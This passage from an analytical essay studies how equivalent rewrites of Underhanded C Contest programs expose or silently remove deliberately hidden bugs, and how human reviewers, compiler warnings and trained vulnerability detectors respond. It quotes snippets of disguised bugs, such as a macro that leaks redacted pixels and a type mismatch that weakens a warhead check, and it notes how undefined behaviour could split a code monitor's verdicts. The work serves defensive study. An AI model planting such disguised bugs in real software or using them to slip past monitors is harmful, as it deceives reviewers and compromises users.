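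| Rewrite | Lospinoso 2015: `sinf` for `isinf` | Stewart 2015: misplaced `goto` | Åkesson 2008: macro without parentheses | Åkesson 2015: two meanings of `float_t` | Eastman 2015: NaN | Meacham 2008: zeros digit by digit |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Renaming variables and functions | hidden | hidden | hidden | hidden | hidden | hidden |
| Reformatting | hidden | hidden | hidden | hidden | hidden | hidden |
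| Converting loops and branches | hidden | visible | hidden | hidden | hidden, or gone if the comparison is reversed | hidden |
| Expanding macros | visible | hidden | visible | hidden | hidden | hidden |
| Inlining functions | hidden | hidden | hidden | gone | hidden | hidden |
| Merging files | hidden | hidden | hidden | does not compile | hidden | hidden |
| Translating to Java | visible | visible | gone | gone | hidden | hidden |

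**Renaming** exposes none of the six, but it can help when the trick depends on names the programmer chose. Matt Bierner's 2015 entry has a function called `error_messager` and a piece of text called `error_message`. The entry passes the text where it should pass the function. That would normally crash the program, but Craver explains that the first bytes of the text, supposedly words in a foreign alphabet, are also valid processor instructions that make the comparison succeed. Renaming the two to `f` and `s` would make them easy to tell apart. Renaming can't separate `isinf` from `sinf`, because both are standard library names, which a renaming tool has to leave unchanged.

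Adding blank lines can change what a program does, even though **reformatting** seems the safest rewrite. Avinash Baliga took second place in 2008 with an error-checking macro that writes the current line number and a message into a buffer. The macro allows 255 characters, but the buffer in `main` holds only 32. The excess overwrites nearby variables, and the newline at the end lands in the mask that should black out the hidden pixels. A newline has the value 10, or 1010 in binary, so two bits of the original survive, too faint to see, as Craver notes.

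The published lines of code show that this bug is fragile. With a two-digit line number, the newline is the 45th character of the message. The buffer takes the first 32 characters and three integers take the next 12, so the newline falls on the first byte of the mask, provided the compiler arranges the variables as Baliga needs. If blank lines push the call from line 99 to line 100, the message becomes one character longer, and the full stop before the newline falls on that byte instead. The full stop has the value 46, so the mask keeps four bits, and the supposedly black rectangle becomes brighter.

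**Converting loops and branches** exposes Gregory Stewart's bug. His function reports failure after it has successfully created new storage, because the `goto` that skips the failure code is inside the wrong pair of braces. Replacing each jump with the `return` it leads to gives this branch:

```c
if (!p) {
    p = malloc(sizeof(struct sample));
    if (!p) return 0;
    memset(p, 0, sizeof(struct sample));
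    *s = p;
    return 0;
}
```

The last line returns the failure code right after the function has handed over a valid block. In the original, the code that did this was split between two labels at the bottom of the function, and the same labels were correct elsewhere in the program.

Loop conversion can also remove a bug by accident. Sean Egan's 2015 entry fills its arrays with `memset(test, -1, bins * sizeof(double))` before reading numbers from a file. `memset` sets each byte to 255, and eight such bytes make a NaN. Someone who thinks the call sets every element to −1 might replace it with a loop that does. If the file contains a character that only resembles a digit, the program fails to read that number and the element keeps its initial value, which is now −1 instead of NaN.

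**Inlining** replaces a function call with the function's body. Done correctly, it exposes Dunphy's broken check. C gives a function its own copy of each argument, so the inlined code needs a second variable, perhaps `err_copy`, which it sets to 1 and never reads. An inliner that omitted the copy would set the real `err`, which would repair the check.

**Translation** to Java exposes Josh Lospinoso's missing letter, since Java doesn't accept a number as a condition. The translator has to write something like `Math.sin(referenceLength) != 0`, and a sine looks out of place in a test for infinity. Java also lacks `goto`, which forces the change that exposes Stewart's bug. Eastman's bug survives in Java, which treats NaN in comparisons the same way as C, but not in ordinary Python, where dividing by zero raises an error before the comparison.

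The accidental repairs happen when the rewriter holds the same belief that misleads the reader. Egan's bug disappears if the rewriter believes that `memset` stores the number −1, and Dunphy's disappears if they believe that a function shares its caller's variable. In each case, the rewriter writes the program that the reader thought was there. Comparing its output with the original's can then locate the bug, although the two programs are no longer equivalent.

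### A macro and a redaction

Rewriting affects Linus Åkesson's 2008 program and John Meacham's very differently. Both programs black out parts of an image but secretly leave information behind. Åkesson's defines the macro `BYTESPERPIXEL` as `3 << (!fits8bits)`, but `fits8bits` needs its own pair of parentheses.

GCC's manual explains this kind of mistake by printing what a macro expands to and then adding the parentheses that C's rules imply. Applied to the number of bytes that Åkesson's program writes for each pixel, the method gives:

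```c
BYTESPERPIXEL(max < 256)
3 << (!max < 256)
3 << ((!max) < 256)
3 << 1
6
```

The comparison is always true, because `!max` is 0 or 1. The same steps reduce `BYTESPERPIXEL(256 > max)` to 3. The main lines of the program then become:

```c
in = alloca(width * height * 3);
out = alloca(width * height * 3);
fread(in, 3, width * height, stdin);
fwrite(out, 6, width * height, stdout);
```

Even a reader who doesn't know operator precedence can see that the program writes twice as much as it reads. Each step is equivalent to the one before, but expansion alone only gets to the second line, where a hurried reader could still miss the problem. The 3 appears next to the 6 only after grouping and simplifying, so a monitor that sees only versions one rewrite away from the original would never see them together.

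A tool that rewrites macro arguments before expanding them can remove the bug without warning. Ramakrishnan and colleagues illustrate their method by changing `x > 0` to `0 < x`, which is safe in an ordinary expression. The same kind of change inside Åkesson's macro turns `BYTESPERPIXEL(max < 256)` into `BYTESPERPIXEL(256 > max)`, which lowers the value from 6 to 3 and removes the leak. If the tool expands macros first, it starts from `(!max) < 256` and changes that to `256 > (!max)`, which has the same value. Replacing the macro with a function, a common way to modernise C, also removes the bug, because a function evaluates its whole argument before using it.

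The leak also requires the original image to come directly after the redacted copy in memory, which happens on the usual machines because the program allocates `in` before `out`. If a rewrite swaps the two allocations, which looks harmless because neither uses the other's result, the original image no longer follows `out`. The program still writes six bytes per pixel, so the mistake remains, but it no longer leaks what its author wanted. In Java, reading past the end of the array would stop the program with an error.

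Meacham's program has no macro to expand and no conversion to misread. Renaming the variables, turning the `for` loop into a `while` loop, moving the `putchar('0')` into a function or translating the program into Java still leaves a program that plainly replaces digits with zeros. A reader who approved the original therefore has no reason to object to any of these versions.

The fault in Meacham's program P is a difference between two outputs that should be the same. Let x and x′ be images that differ only inside the rectangle. If P removed all information about those pixels, P(x) would equal P(x′), because nothing outside the rectangle has changed. But P keeps the number of digits in each value, so P(x) and P(x′) can differ. Any equivalent program Q has the same fault, since Q(x) = P(x) and Q(x′) = P(x′). The requirement that the outputs match comes from the task and isn't stated in the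 code. The Underhanded C Contest defined "blocked out" as "replaced with non-image" and allowed any colour, a pattern or random garbage. The program's black rectangle appears to meet that definition.

Some equivalent versions would give a better hint. Suppose someone regroups the characters into whole numbers and stores the length of each in `n`. Inside the rectangle, the program would then contain:

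```c
for (i = 0; i < n; i++) putchar('0');
```

A reader of this version might ask why the program prints as many zeros as the original number had digits. None of the seven families produces this version, because it requires someone to recognise that a run of digits is one number and to reorganise the program around that fact. A person doing this would be tempted to print a single zero, which is simpler and fixes the leak.

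### Why the 2015 winner is a special case

Renaming variables or changing the loops in Åkesson's 2015 entry doesn't affect its bug, but combining its files can remove the bug, because it depends on two files using different definitions of `float_t`. In `match.c`, `float_t` is an eight-byte number, but in `spectral_contrast.c` it has the standard meaning from `math.h`, usually a four-byte number.

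The C standard says that "All declarations that refer to the same object or function shall have compatible type", as quoted in *DCL23-C. Guarantee that mutually visible identifiers are unique*, a coding rule from the Software Engineering Institute (SEI) at Carnegie Mellon University. A program that breaks this requirement has undefined behaviour. SEI's *DCL40-C. Do not create incompatible declarations of the same function or object* lists further kinds of undefined behaviour that can follow, such as calling a function through the wrong type or reading stored values as a type the standard does not allow. Åkesson's program does both. SEI warns that the effects of violating DCL40-C can range from leaked information to overwritten memory, but it rates violations as low in severity and unlikely to cause a vulnerability, and gives the rule its lowest priority level.

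Undefined behaviour changes which programs count as equivalent. Let S(P, x) be the set of behaviours that the standard allows for program P on input x. A compiler may choose any of them, so it may replace P with Q whenever S(Q, x) ⊆ S(P, x) for every x. If P's behaviour is undefined, S(P, x) contains every possible behaviour, and every program passes this test. A repaired detector would count as a valid replacement for Åkesson's, and so would one that accepts every warhead. But a compiler may not replace the repaired detector with the faulty one, because the repaired detector's behaviour is defined.

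A useful description of the fault has to specify the compiler, its settings and the machine. If c is this combination, P ≡_c Q means that programs P and Q behave identically when compiled and run under c. On an ordinary 64-bit PC, with each file compiled separately, Åkesson's program accepts the same forgeries every time, so its fault is as definite as any other.

The bug may not exist on a different machine. Linux man-pages' *float_t, double_t* (2026) gives three standard possibilities for `float_t`, depending on how the processor carries out floating-point calculations. If it is `float`, the trick works. If it is `double`, the two files agree and the detector works correctly. If it is `long double`, the comparison function treats each number in its arrays as taking up more memory than it does. On 32-bit x86 Linux the difference is twelve bytes instead of eight, so the function reads and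 writes well past the end of the arrays. Åkesson reported that this breaks the program, and that he had checked the trick on 64-bit x86 and 32-bit ARM systems. A reviewer who tested the same source on a machine where `float_t` is not `float` would therefore find either no fault or an obvious one.

Build settings can matter as much as the machine. According to the compiler manual from Texas Instruments (2004), an ordinary link, the step that joins separately compiled files, doesn't check whether the files declare a function with the same types. With link-time optimisation, which analyses the files together, the linker has to check and reports an error if the types differ, even though the program's text is the same. *Project:Toolchain/LTO*, from the Linux distribution Gentoo, describes code that compiles but misbehaves when run as generally the most severe type of bug. It treats some compiler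 warnings as signs that a program may fail under other optimisations or newer compilers.

Combining the two files can expose the bug or remove it unnoticed, depending on how the rewriter does it. Åkesson's `spectral_contrast.c` includes `math.h` for the square-root function `sqrt`. If the rewriter puts both files into one and keeps all the headers, the two definitions of `float_t` collide and compilation fails on a machine where they differ. Adding `match.h` to `spectral_contrast.c` has the same result. If the rewriter moves only the functions into `match.c` and declares `sqrt` by hand, every `float_t` becomes a `double`. The program then compiles and compares the whole spectrum correctly, with no sign that there was ever a bug.

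The obvious ways to resolve the compilation error have different effects. Renaming the type in `match.h`, for example to `real_t`, and using the new name in both files fixes the bug. Using the new name only in `match.h` and `match.c` keeps the bug but makes it easier to see, because `match.c` now passes `real_t` values to a function that expects `float_t`.

If both types end up in one file under different names, the compiler can notice the mismatch. Cooper-Driver, in *Build*, a change to the Trusted Firmware project, notes that version 14 of GCC treats incompatible pointer types as an error, where earlier versions only warned. The change turns the error back into a warning because it had stopped the project's tests from compiling. To keep the original behaviour and satisfy the stricter compiler, a rewriter would have to add explicit conversions:

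```c
return spectral_contrast((float *)t, (float *)r, bins) >= threshold;
```

This line makes it explicit that the program is about to treat eight-byte numbers as four-byte ones, but the behaviour is still undefined. A compiler that can analyse both the caller and the called function may assume that reading a `float` never accesses memory that holds a `double`, and reorder the operations accordingly, so the result can change with the optimisation level.

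If a monitor rejects the original and accepts the supposedly equivalent merged file, both verdicts may be correct. In that case, it would be a mistake to treat the disagreement as an error, and training a model to give both programs the same answer would teach it to get one of them wrong. An attacker can most easily arrange such cases in programs with undefined behaviour, because the usual rules for rewriting C assume that there is none.

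### Bugs in the text and bugs in the idea

One way to predict whether rewriting will expose a bug is to describe in plain English exactly what the code does. Stewart's function reports failure when it has succeeded. Lospinoso's test for a second infinite number calculates a sine. Åkesson's 2008 program reads three bytes for each pixel and writes six. In each case an accurate description reveals the bug, so the text of the code must have been hiding it. The same is true of the assignment in the Linux kernel backdoor, which makes the caller root. Some equivalent version will expose bugs like these, though it may take several rewrites to reach it.

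Meacham's program replaces every digit in the rectangle with a zero. That description is just as accurate, and it sounds like a correct redaction. Stephen Dolan's 2015 entry adds up squared differences and subtracts the largest, which sounds reasonable to anyone who doesn't think about rounding. Domenico Andreoli's 2014 program downloads the user's profile picture when a message matches a surveillance request. These bugs are in the idea behind each program, so a reader who correctly understands what the code does still has to realise that an image file can leak information through the length of its numbers, or that the user can watch for the download.

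Eastman's bug is closer to this second group. An accurate description of his last line, "rejects the warhead if the correlation is below the threshold, and otherwise accepts it", sounds right. But adding one case, the NaN, exposes the bug, and a tool could do that without understanding nuclear inspections. No comparably simple addition exposes Meacham's leak.

The 2015 winner hides its bug in the type name `float_t`, which stands for different types in its two files. A description of the whole program would reveal that one part passes eight-byte numbers and another reads them as four-byte numbers, but separate descriptions of the two files would both sound correct. Replacing each `float_t` with the type it stands for on a given machine would make the mismatch visible without changing the program's behaviour there. A tool that does this has to follow the included headers, because the visible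 text alone doesn't show which `float_t` each file uses.

Both kinds were common among the more than 100 entries in the 2008 contest. Craver says that many programs appended the original image to the output, which a plain description would reveal. Many others scrambled the hidden pixels with a pseudo-random mask but deliberately chose the generator's starting value badly, so that an attacker could recover the mask. If such a program takes its starting value from the clock, so does every equivalent version, and a reader who doesn't know that an attacker can guess the time will find nothing wrong with any of them.

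## What reformatting, compiler warnings and human review catch

Wheeler's 2020 study for the Institute for Defense Analyses is the closest thing to a measurement on real underhanded code. He examined which entries to the 2004 vote-counting contest a few simple countermeasures would catch. The contest's website had 41 scored programs in C and C++, each with a short explanation of its trick. One contained no attack, which left 40, including two that Wheeler had written.

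He first located the lines that made each program miscount. In 25 of the 40, the trick belonged to one of five groups. Nine programs misused macros, seven confused the letters l and O with the digits 1 and 0, five read or wrote outside an array, two hid live code in a comment, and two used `=` for `==`. He then chose five countermeasures, partly to fit these groups. The marks in his appendix add up as follows:

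| Countermeasure | Entries caught, of 40 | Share | Basis |
|---|---|---|---|
| The gcc compiler with many extra warnings turned on | 15 | 37.5% | ran it on every entry |
| Macros only where nothing else works, with names in capitals and full parentheses | 9 | 22.5% | judged from the code |
| No names that differ from a number only by l for 1 or O for 0 | 8 | 20% | judged from the code |
| Address Sanitizer, which reports when a running program uses memory it shouldn't | 5 | 12.5% | mostly judged from the code |
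| Syntax colouring, and a new line after every comment | 2 | 5% | mostly judged from the code |
| At least one of the five | 30 | 75% | |

gcc should have caught one more entry, but its check for misleading indentation had a bug, which Wheeler reported. Of the other nine, he thought six would make a reviewer suspicious anyway, for example because of an unusual amount of repetition. Only three programs, or 7.5%, would get past both the countermeasures and a suspicious reader.

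The compiler's 15 is the most reliable number, because he counted a warning only if it pointed to the faulty line and revealed the fault. The 75% is weaker evidence, since he picked the countermeasures after studying the entries. He defends this by saying he only wanted to show that a few simple measures can often work. The study does show that, but it doesn't predict how well they would work on new programs. It also includes no honest programs, so it gives no rate of false alarms.

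The entrants of 2004 weren't trying to evade these tools either, since the version of gcc in the study came out fifteen years after the contest. An attacker today can run the compiler first and rewrite whatever it flags. gcc warned about both entries that used `=` for `==`, but the kernel attacker of 2003 had avoided that warning by adding a pair of parentheses.

Wheeler marked 15 of the 40 programs as likely to make an experienced programmer suspicious. The five measures caught 21 of the other 25, so clumsy entries don't explain the result. The compiler, gcc, did worse on the nine programs with a trigger, which miscount only on election day. It caught two of them, and one of those was a modified copy of the other. The other 31 programs can go wrong on any day, so good tests would expose them.

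The contest judges and the tools disagreed about which programs were well hidden. Michal Zalewski's had the highest score, 7.3 out of 10. It gives a tenth of all votes to Bush, using a macro that declares its own variable `t` where one of that name already exists, and gcc has a warning for exactly this. Jared Sohn's program scored only 3.7 but got past all five countermeasures with this test for a Nader vote:

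```c
((Vote == 'n') || (Vote == 'n'))
```

The second letter should be a capital N. Because it isn't, a vote typed as a capital N goes to "Other". Shortening the line to `(Vote == 'n')` would be an equivalent rewrite and might lead a reader to ask what happens to capitals.

### Reformatting as a detector

Wheeler also recommends reformatting all source code to a standard style that the attacker doesn't control, though he scored only the part that concerns comments. Reformatting normally preserves the program's semantics, because layout rarely matters to a C compiler. Readers use indentation to see which lines belong together, so an attacker can mislead them with it. A reformatter replaces any misleading indentation with indentation based on the program's actual structure.

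Kristian Nielsen's entry, the one that gcc should have caught, is a good example. In outline, with simplified names, it changes like this:

```c
/* as written */
while (isspace(next = getchar()))
if (next == 'K')
    kerry++;

/* reformatted */
while (isspace(next = getchar()))
    if (next == 'K')
        kerry++;
```

The loop in the first version has no braces, so it repeats the statement that follows it, however that statement is indented. That statement is the check for a Kerry vote. The check runs only when the program has just read a space, so it never succeeds. A reader will assume instead that the loop skips spaces and that the program then checks the vote.

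Reformatting also exposes live code that looks like a comment. Michael Moore's entry closes a long comment early, follows it with working code laid out like more of the comment, and puts a second closing mark where the reader expects the first. Syntax colouring reveals this too, but Wheeler doesn't trust it on its own. When he opened a Python program with a fake comment in a colouring editor, he didn't notice the different colour.

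Only three of the 40 entries, Nielsen's and the two with code in comments, seem to depend on layout. Renaming every variable would affect all eight entries that rely on l or O, and expanding macros would affect another nine. For example, Oleg Kibirev's program adds to Bush's total with `b+=l;`, which uses the letter l rather than the digit 1. (Wheeler's appendix mistakenly prints the letter in both the faulty line and the correction.) Renaming would produce something like `b+=v3;`, which nobody would read as adding one. Together with reformatting, these rewrites would change the misleading text in half of the 40 programs, although nobody has tested how many readers would then find the fault.

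*Atoms of Confusion in Java* reports an experiment in which students predicted what short programs would print. When the programs had neither braces nor indentation to show which lines belonged together, 17 of 33 answers were wrong, compared with none of 26 when the programs were indented. The study's figure of 56 times more mistakes comes from this comparison and is very imprecise (95% confidence interval 3 to 999). When the programs had braces but bad indentation, only 2 of 33 answers were wrong. A formatter that also adds braces may therefore protect readers better than one that only moves lines.

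Wheeler warns that the people who write reformatters don't expect malicious input, and that an attacker might exploit bugs in the tools. He suggests compiling the code before and after reformatting to check that its meaning hasn't changed. This check could also flag a program like Avinash Baliga's, whose hidden bug depends on a line number.

### Readers who know the code is malicious

Wheeler knew the programs were supposed to be malicious, and he had the organisers' explanation of each trick. He still found some faults hard to locate, partly because four of the explanations were wrong, misleading or about code that wasn't there.

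The explanation of Ryan Cumings's program mistakenly blamed a swapped O and 0. Travis Fisher's program was harmless as published. The attack was in a compiler option that redefined `isspace`, the standard test for a space, as a test for the letter K. Nobody had kept the original command, so the organiser supplied a substitute after Wheeler asked about it. The explanation of Geir Thomassen's program, which Wheeler excluded, mentions a macro and a comma operator that the program doesn't contain, and the program appears to count correctly. Brad Grzesiak's program was explained as "gets instead of equals". It never calls C's `gets` function, and the organisers probably meant that it assigns a value where it should compare.

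Only the Cumings explanation is clearly a misreading of the code. Fisher's and Thomassen's attacks were missing from the published files, and Grzesiak's explanation was badly worded. But these mistakes had been on a public website for more than a decade, beside programs that everyone knew to be malicious. The 40 entries may include another attack that doesn't work, since Wheeler could not get Kenneth Davis's program to miscount. He kept it in the set, and it is one of the 15 that gcc caught.

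He found the faults easier to spot as he went on. This may be only because the contest lists its entries roughly from hardest to easiest, but he suspects that practice also helps and suggests training reviewers on samples.

Wheeler's evidence comes from one early contest, and many of its tricks are simple. Many winners of the Underhanded Crypto Contest instead exploited technical weaknesses in cryptography. These flaws are in a program's design, so rules about macros or variable names won't expose them, and Wheeler concludes that specialists have to review such code in depth. He also advises defenders to keep the details of some countermeasures secret, so that attackers can't test a program against all of them.

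### Rewriting code to make it clearer

Experiments on atoms of confusion, small patterns that programmers often misread, test rewriting more directly because they compare equivalent versions of the same code. In *Understanding misunderstandings in source code*, Gopstein, Iannacone and colleagues (2017) took 19 candidate patterns from winners of the obfuscated C contest. They asked 73 participants to work out by hand what short programs would print. Some programs contained one of the patterns, and others used a clearer equivalent. Fifteen of the patterns caused significantly more errors than their replacements.

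Several tricks used in underhanded programs are on Gopstein and colleagues' list of confusing code patterns. An assignment inside an `if` condition, as in the kernel backdoor, had an effect size of 0.64, and they count 0.5 as large. Macros that combine unexpectedly with the surrounding code, as in Åkesson's 2008 program, had an effect size of 0.36.

In a second experiment, 43 people worked through four whole programs from the obfuscated contest. The researchers had cleaned up the layout and replaced the names with neutral ones, so any remaining difference came from the atoms. People who got the versions without atoms gave up a quarter as often and were five times as likely to get the entire output right. They still made some mistakes, for instance because they didn't know that C initializes certain variables to zero.

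The Java study found a similar benefit. Participants got 37% of the answers wrong with an atom and 13% without. But a replacement can be confusing too. In Java and C, the number `013` means 11, because the leading zero marks it as octal. The study's replacement was a function call that converts "13" from base 8, and 10 of 22 answers were still wrong. When participants compared the two versions, more of them found the replacement confusing than the original.

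A reader can give the right answer without understanding the code. In *Thinking Aloud about Confusing Code*, Gopstein, Fayard and colleagues (2020) listened to 14 programmers, nine of them professionals, each work through eight short programs. All 17 wrong answers were for versions with a confusing pattern, and four students gave 14 of those answers. In seven of the 17 cases, the pattern was only one of the causes of the error or not a cause at all.

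One professional in this study got the following condition right by luck:

```c
0 && 1 || 2
2 || 1 && 0
```

He saw only the first line. He believed that `&&` ("and") and `||` ("or") have equal priority and that C reads them from left to right, but `&&` has higher priority. On the first line, his rule still gives the correct answer, "true". The second line swaps the two sides of each operator, which doesn't change the result, but his rule would now give "false". An equivalent version can therefore reveal that a reader has misunderstood the language, even if their first answer was correct.

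Programmers are often reluctant to rewrite confusing code that works, according to a survey cited by Abdelsalam and colleagues, but language models can do much of this work. Van de Wetering and colleagues asked ChatGPT and GitHub Copilot to remove confusing patterns, called atoms, from three C++ libraries, with 20 samples for each pattern. The models removed most patterns reliably but had trouble with some, such as variables reused for a second purpose. The researchers checked the new versions with each library's own tests. This check would be too weak for underhanded code, because ordinary tests don't include the trigger and so can't show whether a rewrite has accidentally removed the backdoor.

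All of these experiments asked people to work out what a program does, not whether it was safe. Someone predicting the output of a four-line program will look at every line, but a reviewer with a long patch may skip the one that matters. The researchers also left out code with undefined behaviour and code that depends on complex library functions. This excludes the trick in the 2015 warhead program, where two files use different sizes for the same number.

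### Reviewers and planted vulnerabilities

Studies of code review come closer to the real task, although the flaws they use aren't disguised. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) had 150 people review a Java code change online. Most were software engineers, and 65% said they reviewed code every day. The change contained two vulnerabilities: an error message that revealed sensitive information, and a cryptographic algorithm no longer considered safe.

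One group received no special instructions, and the others were told to look for security problems. Of those told to look, one group also received a general checklist and another received a short one written for these flaws. People who were told to look for security problems were eight times as likely to find a vulnerability, but neither checklist improved the results significantly.

Reviewers apparently miss many flaws like these because they aren't thinking about security. But attention may not be enough when the author has disguised the flaw, since even contest judges who expect malice have trouble finding some of the faults. No study here gave reviewers both the original and a rewritten version of an underhanded program, so how much rewriting such code helps human reviewers is still unmeasured.

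An experiment of this kind would need to control for the effect of looking twice. In an earlier study that Braz and colleagues describe, many developers who had missed a vulnerability found it after the researchers told them it existed. But the study had no comparison group, so some of them may have found it simply because they looked again. Reviewers shown an equivalent version of a program could also find a bug for that reason. To show that the rewrite itself helps, researchers would have to compare reviewers who see a second version with reviewers who see the first version again.

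## How trained detectors respond to rewritten code

A trained detector is a model that takes a function as input and outputs the probability that the function is vulnerable. Most detectors keep no memory of earlier functions and give the same output for the same text every time, so if the output changes after a rewrite, the rewrite caused the change. Human reviewers who see a second version of a program, by contrast, may find a bug only because they looked twice.

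### Counting changed verdicts

Researchers give a detector a function and several equivalent versions, and measure the share of versions whose verdict differs from the original's. *On the Generalizability of Neural Program Models* (Rabin, Bui and colleagues, 2020) calls this share the prediction change percentage. Its models suggested names for Java methods instead of looking for bugs, but the measurement is the same. In one example, renaming a variable from `other` to `var0` changed a model's suggestion from `compareTo`, the correct name, to `getCount`.

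Rabin and colleagues also recorded whether each change made a correct answer wrong or a wrong answer correct. A detector has only two answers, so every changed verdict does one or the other. Let b be the share of versions on which a correct verdict becomes wrong, and c the share on which a wrong verdict becomes correct. Then:

share of changed verdicts = b + c

change in accuracy = c − b

Many studies of detectors report only the change in accuracy after rewriting, which can hide how many verdicts changed. A loss of two points could mean that 2% of verdicts became wrong and none became correct, or that 26% became wrong and 24% became correct. The corrections in the second case help only if there is some way to tell them from the new mistakes.

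### Training on rewritten code

In 2023, Risse and Böhme trained and tested six small language models for code, including CodeBERT, UniXcoder, VulBERTa and PLBART, on detecting vulnerabilities. They used two datasets. The main one, Devign, has about 26,400 C functions from the open-source video software FFmpeg and the open-source machine emulator QEMU, and 45.6% of them are labelled "vulnerable".

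The study used 11 rewrites. One renames the function and another renames its parameters. Five insert something: white space, a comment, code that never runs, a call to an extra function, or code from the training set disguised as a comment. Three others remove all comments, reorder the parameters, or move the body into a separate function. The last applies one of these ten at random. Reordering the parameters is equivalent only if every caller reorders its arguments too, which a detector that reads one function at a time can't check.

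Their first algorithm measures how rewriting the test functions changes a model's score, and whether training on rewritten functions helps. It compares each result with the score of a model trained and tested on the original code. The second dataset, VulDeePecker, has a smaller share of vulnerable samples than the first (28.7%), so they scored models on it by F1, which combines precision (the share of alarms that are correct) with recall (the share of vulnerable functions found).

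| Training functions | Test functions | Accuracy on Devign | F1 on VulDeePecker |
|---|---|---|---|
| original | rewritten | −2.5 points | −4.3 points |
| rewritten in the same way as the test functions | rewritten | −0.7 points | −0.8 points |
| rewritten in a different way | rewritten | −3.2 points | −5.9 points |

Training on the same rewrite used in testing recovered an average of 69% of each model's lost performance on Devign and 66% on VulDeePecker. Training on a different rewrite made the loss worse. The models had apparently learned to ignore one change, such as an added comment, but not to ignore changes that don't affect the program in general. Training on a random mixture of the other rewrites recovered part of the lost performance, perhaps because some rewrites resemble each other. Training a detector this way therefore protects mainly against rewrites like those in the training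 data.

The effects also varied by rewrite. Renaming, adding white space and removing comments each lowered accuracy by about one point or less. Calling an extra function lowered it by 1.8 to 18.1 points, depending on the model. Pasting in training code as a comment, which a C compiler discards, lowered it by 2.1 to 11.5 points.

A detector that labels every function safe never changes its verdict, so stability alone doesn't show that a detector is good. The second algorithm therefore tests whether detectors respond to a change that should affect the verdict. Risse and Böhme paired about 13,100 vulnerable functions with their patched versions. The average accuracy of the six models fell from 65.7% on the ordinary test to 43.4% on these pairs.

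A detector that gave both functions in every pair the same answer would score exactly 50%. Three of the models scored less than that because they flagged patched functions more often than vulnerable ones. Training on such pairs raised the average to 59.8%, but these models scored only 55.9% on the ordinary test. So the detectors often changed their verdicts on rewrites that left the program's behaviour the same, and they often failed to identify which function in a pair had the bug.

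### The 2025 re-evaluation

Li, Qi and colleagues (2025), in *Revisiting Pre-trained Language Models for Vulnerability Detection*, repeated such tests with more accurate labels and a wider range of models. They also split the functions by date, training the models on older code and testing them on newer code. A random split can put nearly identical functions in both the training and test sets.

Their four rewrites change the structure of the code instead of adding text to it. One negates the condition of a branch and swaps the two outcomes. Applied to the end of Peter Eastman's warhead detector, it gives:

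```c
/* before */
if (correlation < threshold) return 0;
else return 1;

/* after */
if (!(correlation < threshold)) return 1;
else return 0;
```

These are equivalent even if the correlation is NaN, so Eastman's bug survives.

The other rewrites split a compound condition into separate branches, convert one kind of loop into another, and reverse comparisons, for example from `a < b` to `b > a`. If a rewrite could be made in several places in a function, the researchers made it in each place separately, which produced 48,182 rewritten versions of 23,144 functions.

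Negating branches reduced performance by an average of 15.8%, while splitting conditions reduced it by only 1.3%. Li and colleagues suggest that negation has a larger effect because it moves whole blocks of code, which puts related lines further apart. The most robust model, UniXcoder, lost an average of only 0.1% across the rewrites. The researchers attribute this to its original training, which included training it to give related inputs similar internal representations.

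But in the 2023 study, UniXcoder lost the most accuracy of any model on Devign, 4.3 points on average. Many of the rewrites in that study inserted text, whereas these rearrange branches, loops and comparisons. A detector can evidently be robust to one kind of rewrite and sensitive to another, so calling a model "robust" means little without saying which rewrites it was tested on.

Accuracy on ordinary code doesn't predict robustness either, according to *SoK* (2025), a survey of security problems in AI tools for code. *Characterizing Robustness in Semantic Code Clone Detection* (2026) reports the same for models that are trained to judge whether two pieces of code do the same job, and so should be good at recognising equivalent programs. In 21 of 25 tests where such a model started with an F1 above 90%, a combination of rewrites lowered it by at least 10 points.

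Even formatting can affect performance if it differs from the training data. PDBERT, the best of the small models in the 2025 study, had trained on code with line breaks, and removing them from the test functions reduced its performance by about 6.9%. Replacing every variable name and piece of text with a neutral label such as `VAR0` reduced the models' performance by only 1% on average. The models missed more vulnerabilities, but they also raised fewer false alarms, which partly offset the loss.

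The study also shows why an extra alarm from a rewritten version is weak evidence. Of 25,536 newly collected functions, only 646 were vulnerable. PDBERT found 61% of these but also flagged 18% of the others, so only 8% of its alarms were correct. A reviewer who rejected a program whenever any version of it set off an alarm would mostly collect more false alarms.

### Voting over equivalent versions

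Hort, Vidziunas and Moonen (2025), in *Semantic-Preserving Transformations as Mutation Operators*, tested whether a detector's predictions on equivalent versions of a program can correct its prediction on the original. They first looked for rewrites to reuse and found 94 in 28 papers. Renaming variables was by far the most common, appearing in 25 of the papers. Code was available for 19 of the papers, and seven of these had rewrites for C or C++. They chose four papers that offered several rewrites each, which gave them 39 to try.

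They then checked up to 20 outputs of each rewrite by hand, and found that 23 of the 39 changed what the program does. One of the faulty rewrites moves the declaration of a variable into a loop, which fails if a later loop uses the same variable. In outline:

```c
/* before */
int i;
for (i = 0; i < n; i++) a[i] = 0;
for (i = 0; i < n; i++) b[i] = 0;

/* after */
for (int i = 0; i < n; i++) a[i] = 0;
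for (i = 0; i < n; i++) b[i] = 0;
```

In the second version, `i` no longer exists when the second loop begins. A compiler would catch this error, but not every change in behaviour. The other 16 rewrites may have faults too, since the researchers looked at only a sample of outputs. Rewrites of underhanded code are even harder to check, because a rewrite that works on ordinary functions may remove a bug that depends on undefined behaviour.

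Hort and colleagues applied the 16 rewrites one at a time to the 2,732 test functions in Devign, which produced 4 to 12 versions of each function, with an average of 6.3. Four of the rewrites applied to every function, and these change only white space, comments or unused code. Most of the others rarely applied, some to as few as three functions. They tested two detectors, VulBERTa and PLBART, that other researchers had already trained on Devign.

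The verdict changed between the original and the rewritten version in 49% of cases, from vulnerable to safe in 25% and from safe to vulnerable in 24%.

The researchers then combined the verdicts in three ways. A majority vote counts each version once. Averaging uses the detector's probabilities, so confident verdicts count for more than marginal ones. Weighting gives each rewrite its own weight, chosen to maximise accuracy on a separate set of functions. The table shows accuracy in per cent. "All versions" includes the original function.

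| Way of combining verdicts | VulBERTa, all versions | PLBART, all versions | Both detectors, original only | Both detectors, all versions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None: one detector, original only | 64.71 | 61.79 | – | – |
| Majority vote, ties count as safe | 51.43 | 48.13 | 58.86 | 52.12 |
| Majority vote, ties count as vulnerable | 51.39 | 47.91 | 54.54 | 51.79 |
| Average probability | 52.49 | 50.84 | 62.52 | 52.12 |
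| Weighted verdicts | 52.34 | 54.28 | 61.79 | 60.03 |
| Weighted probabilities | 52.12 | 59.19 | 61.75 | 60.61 |

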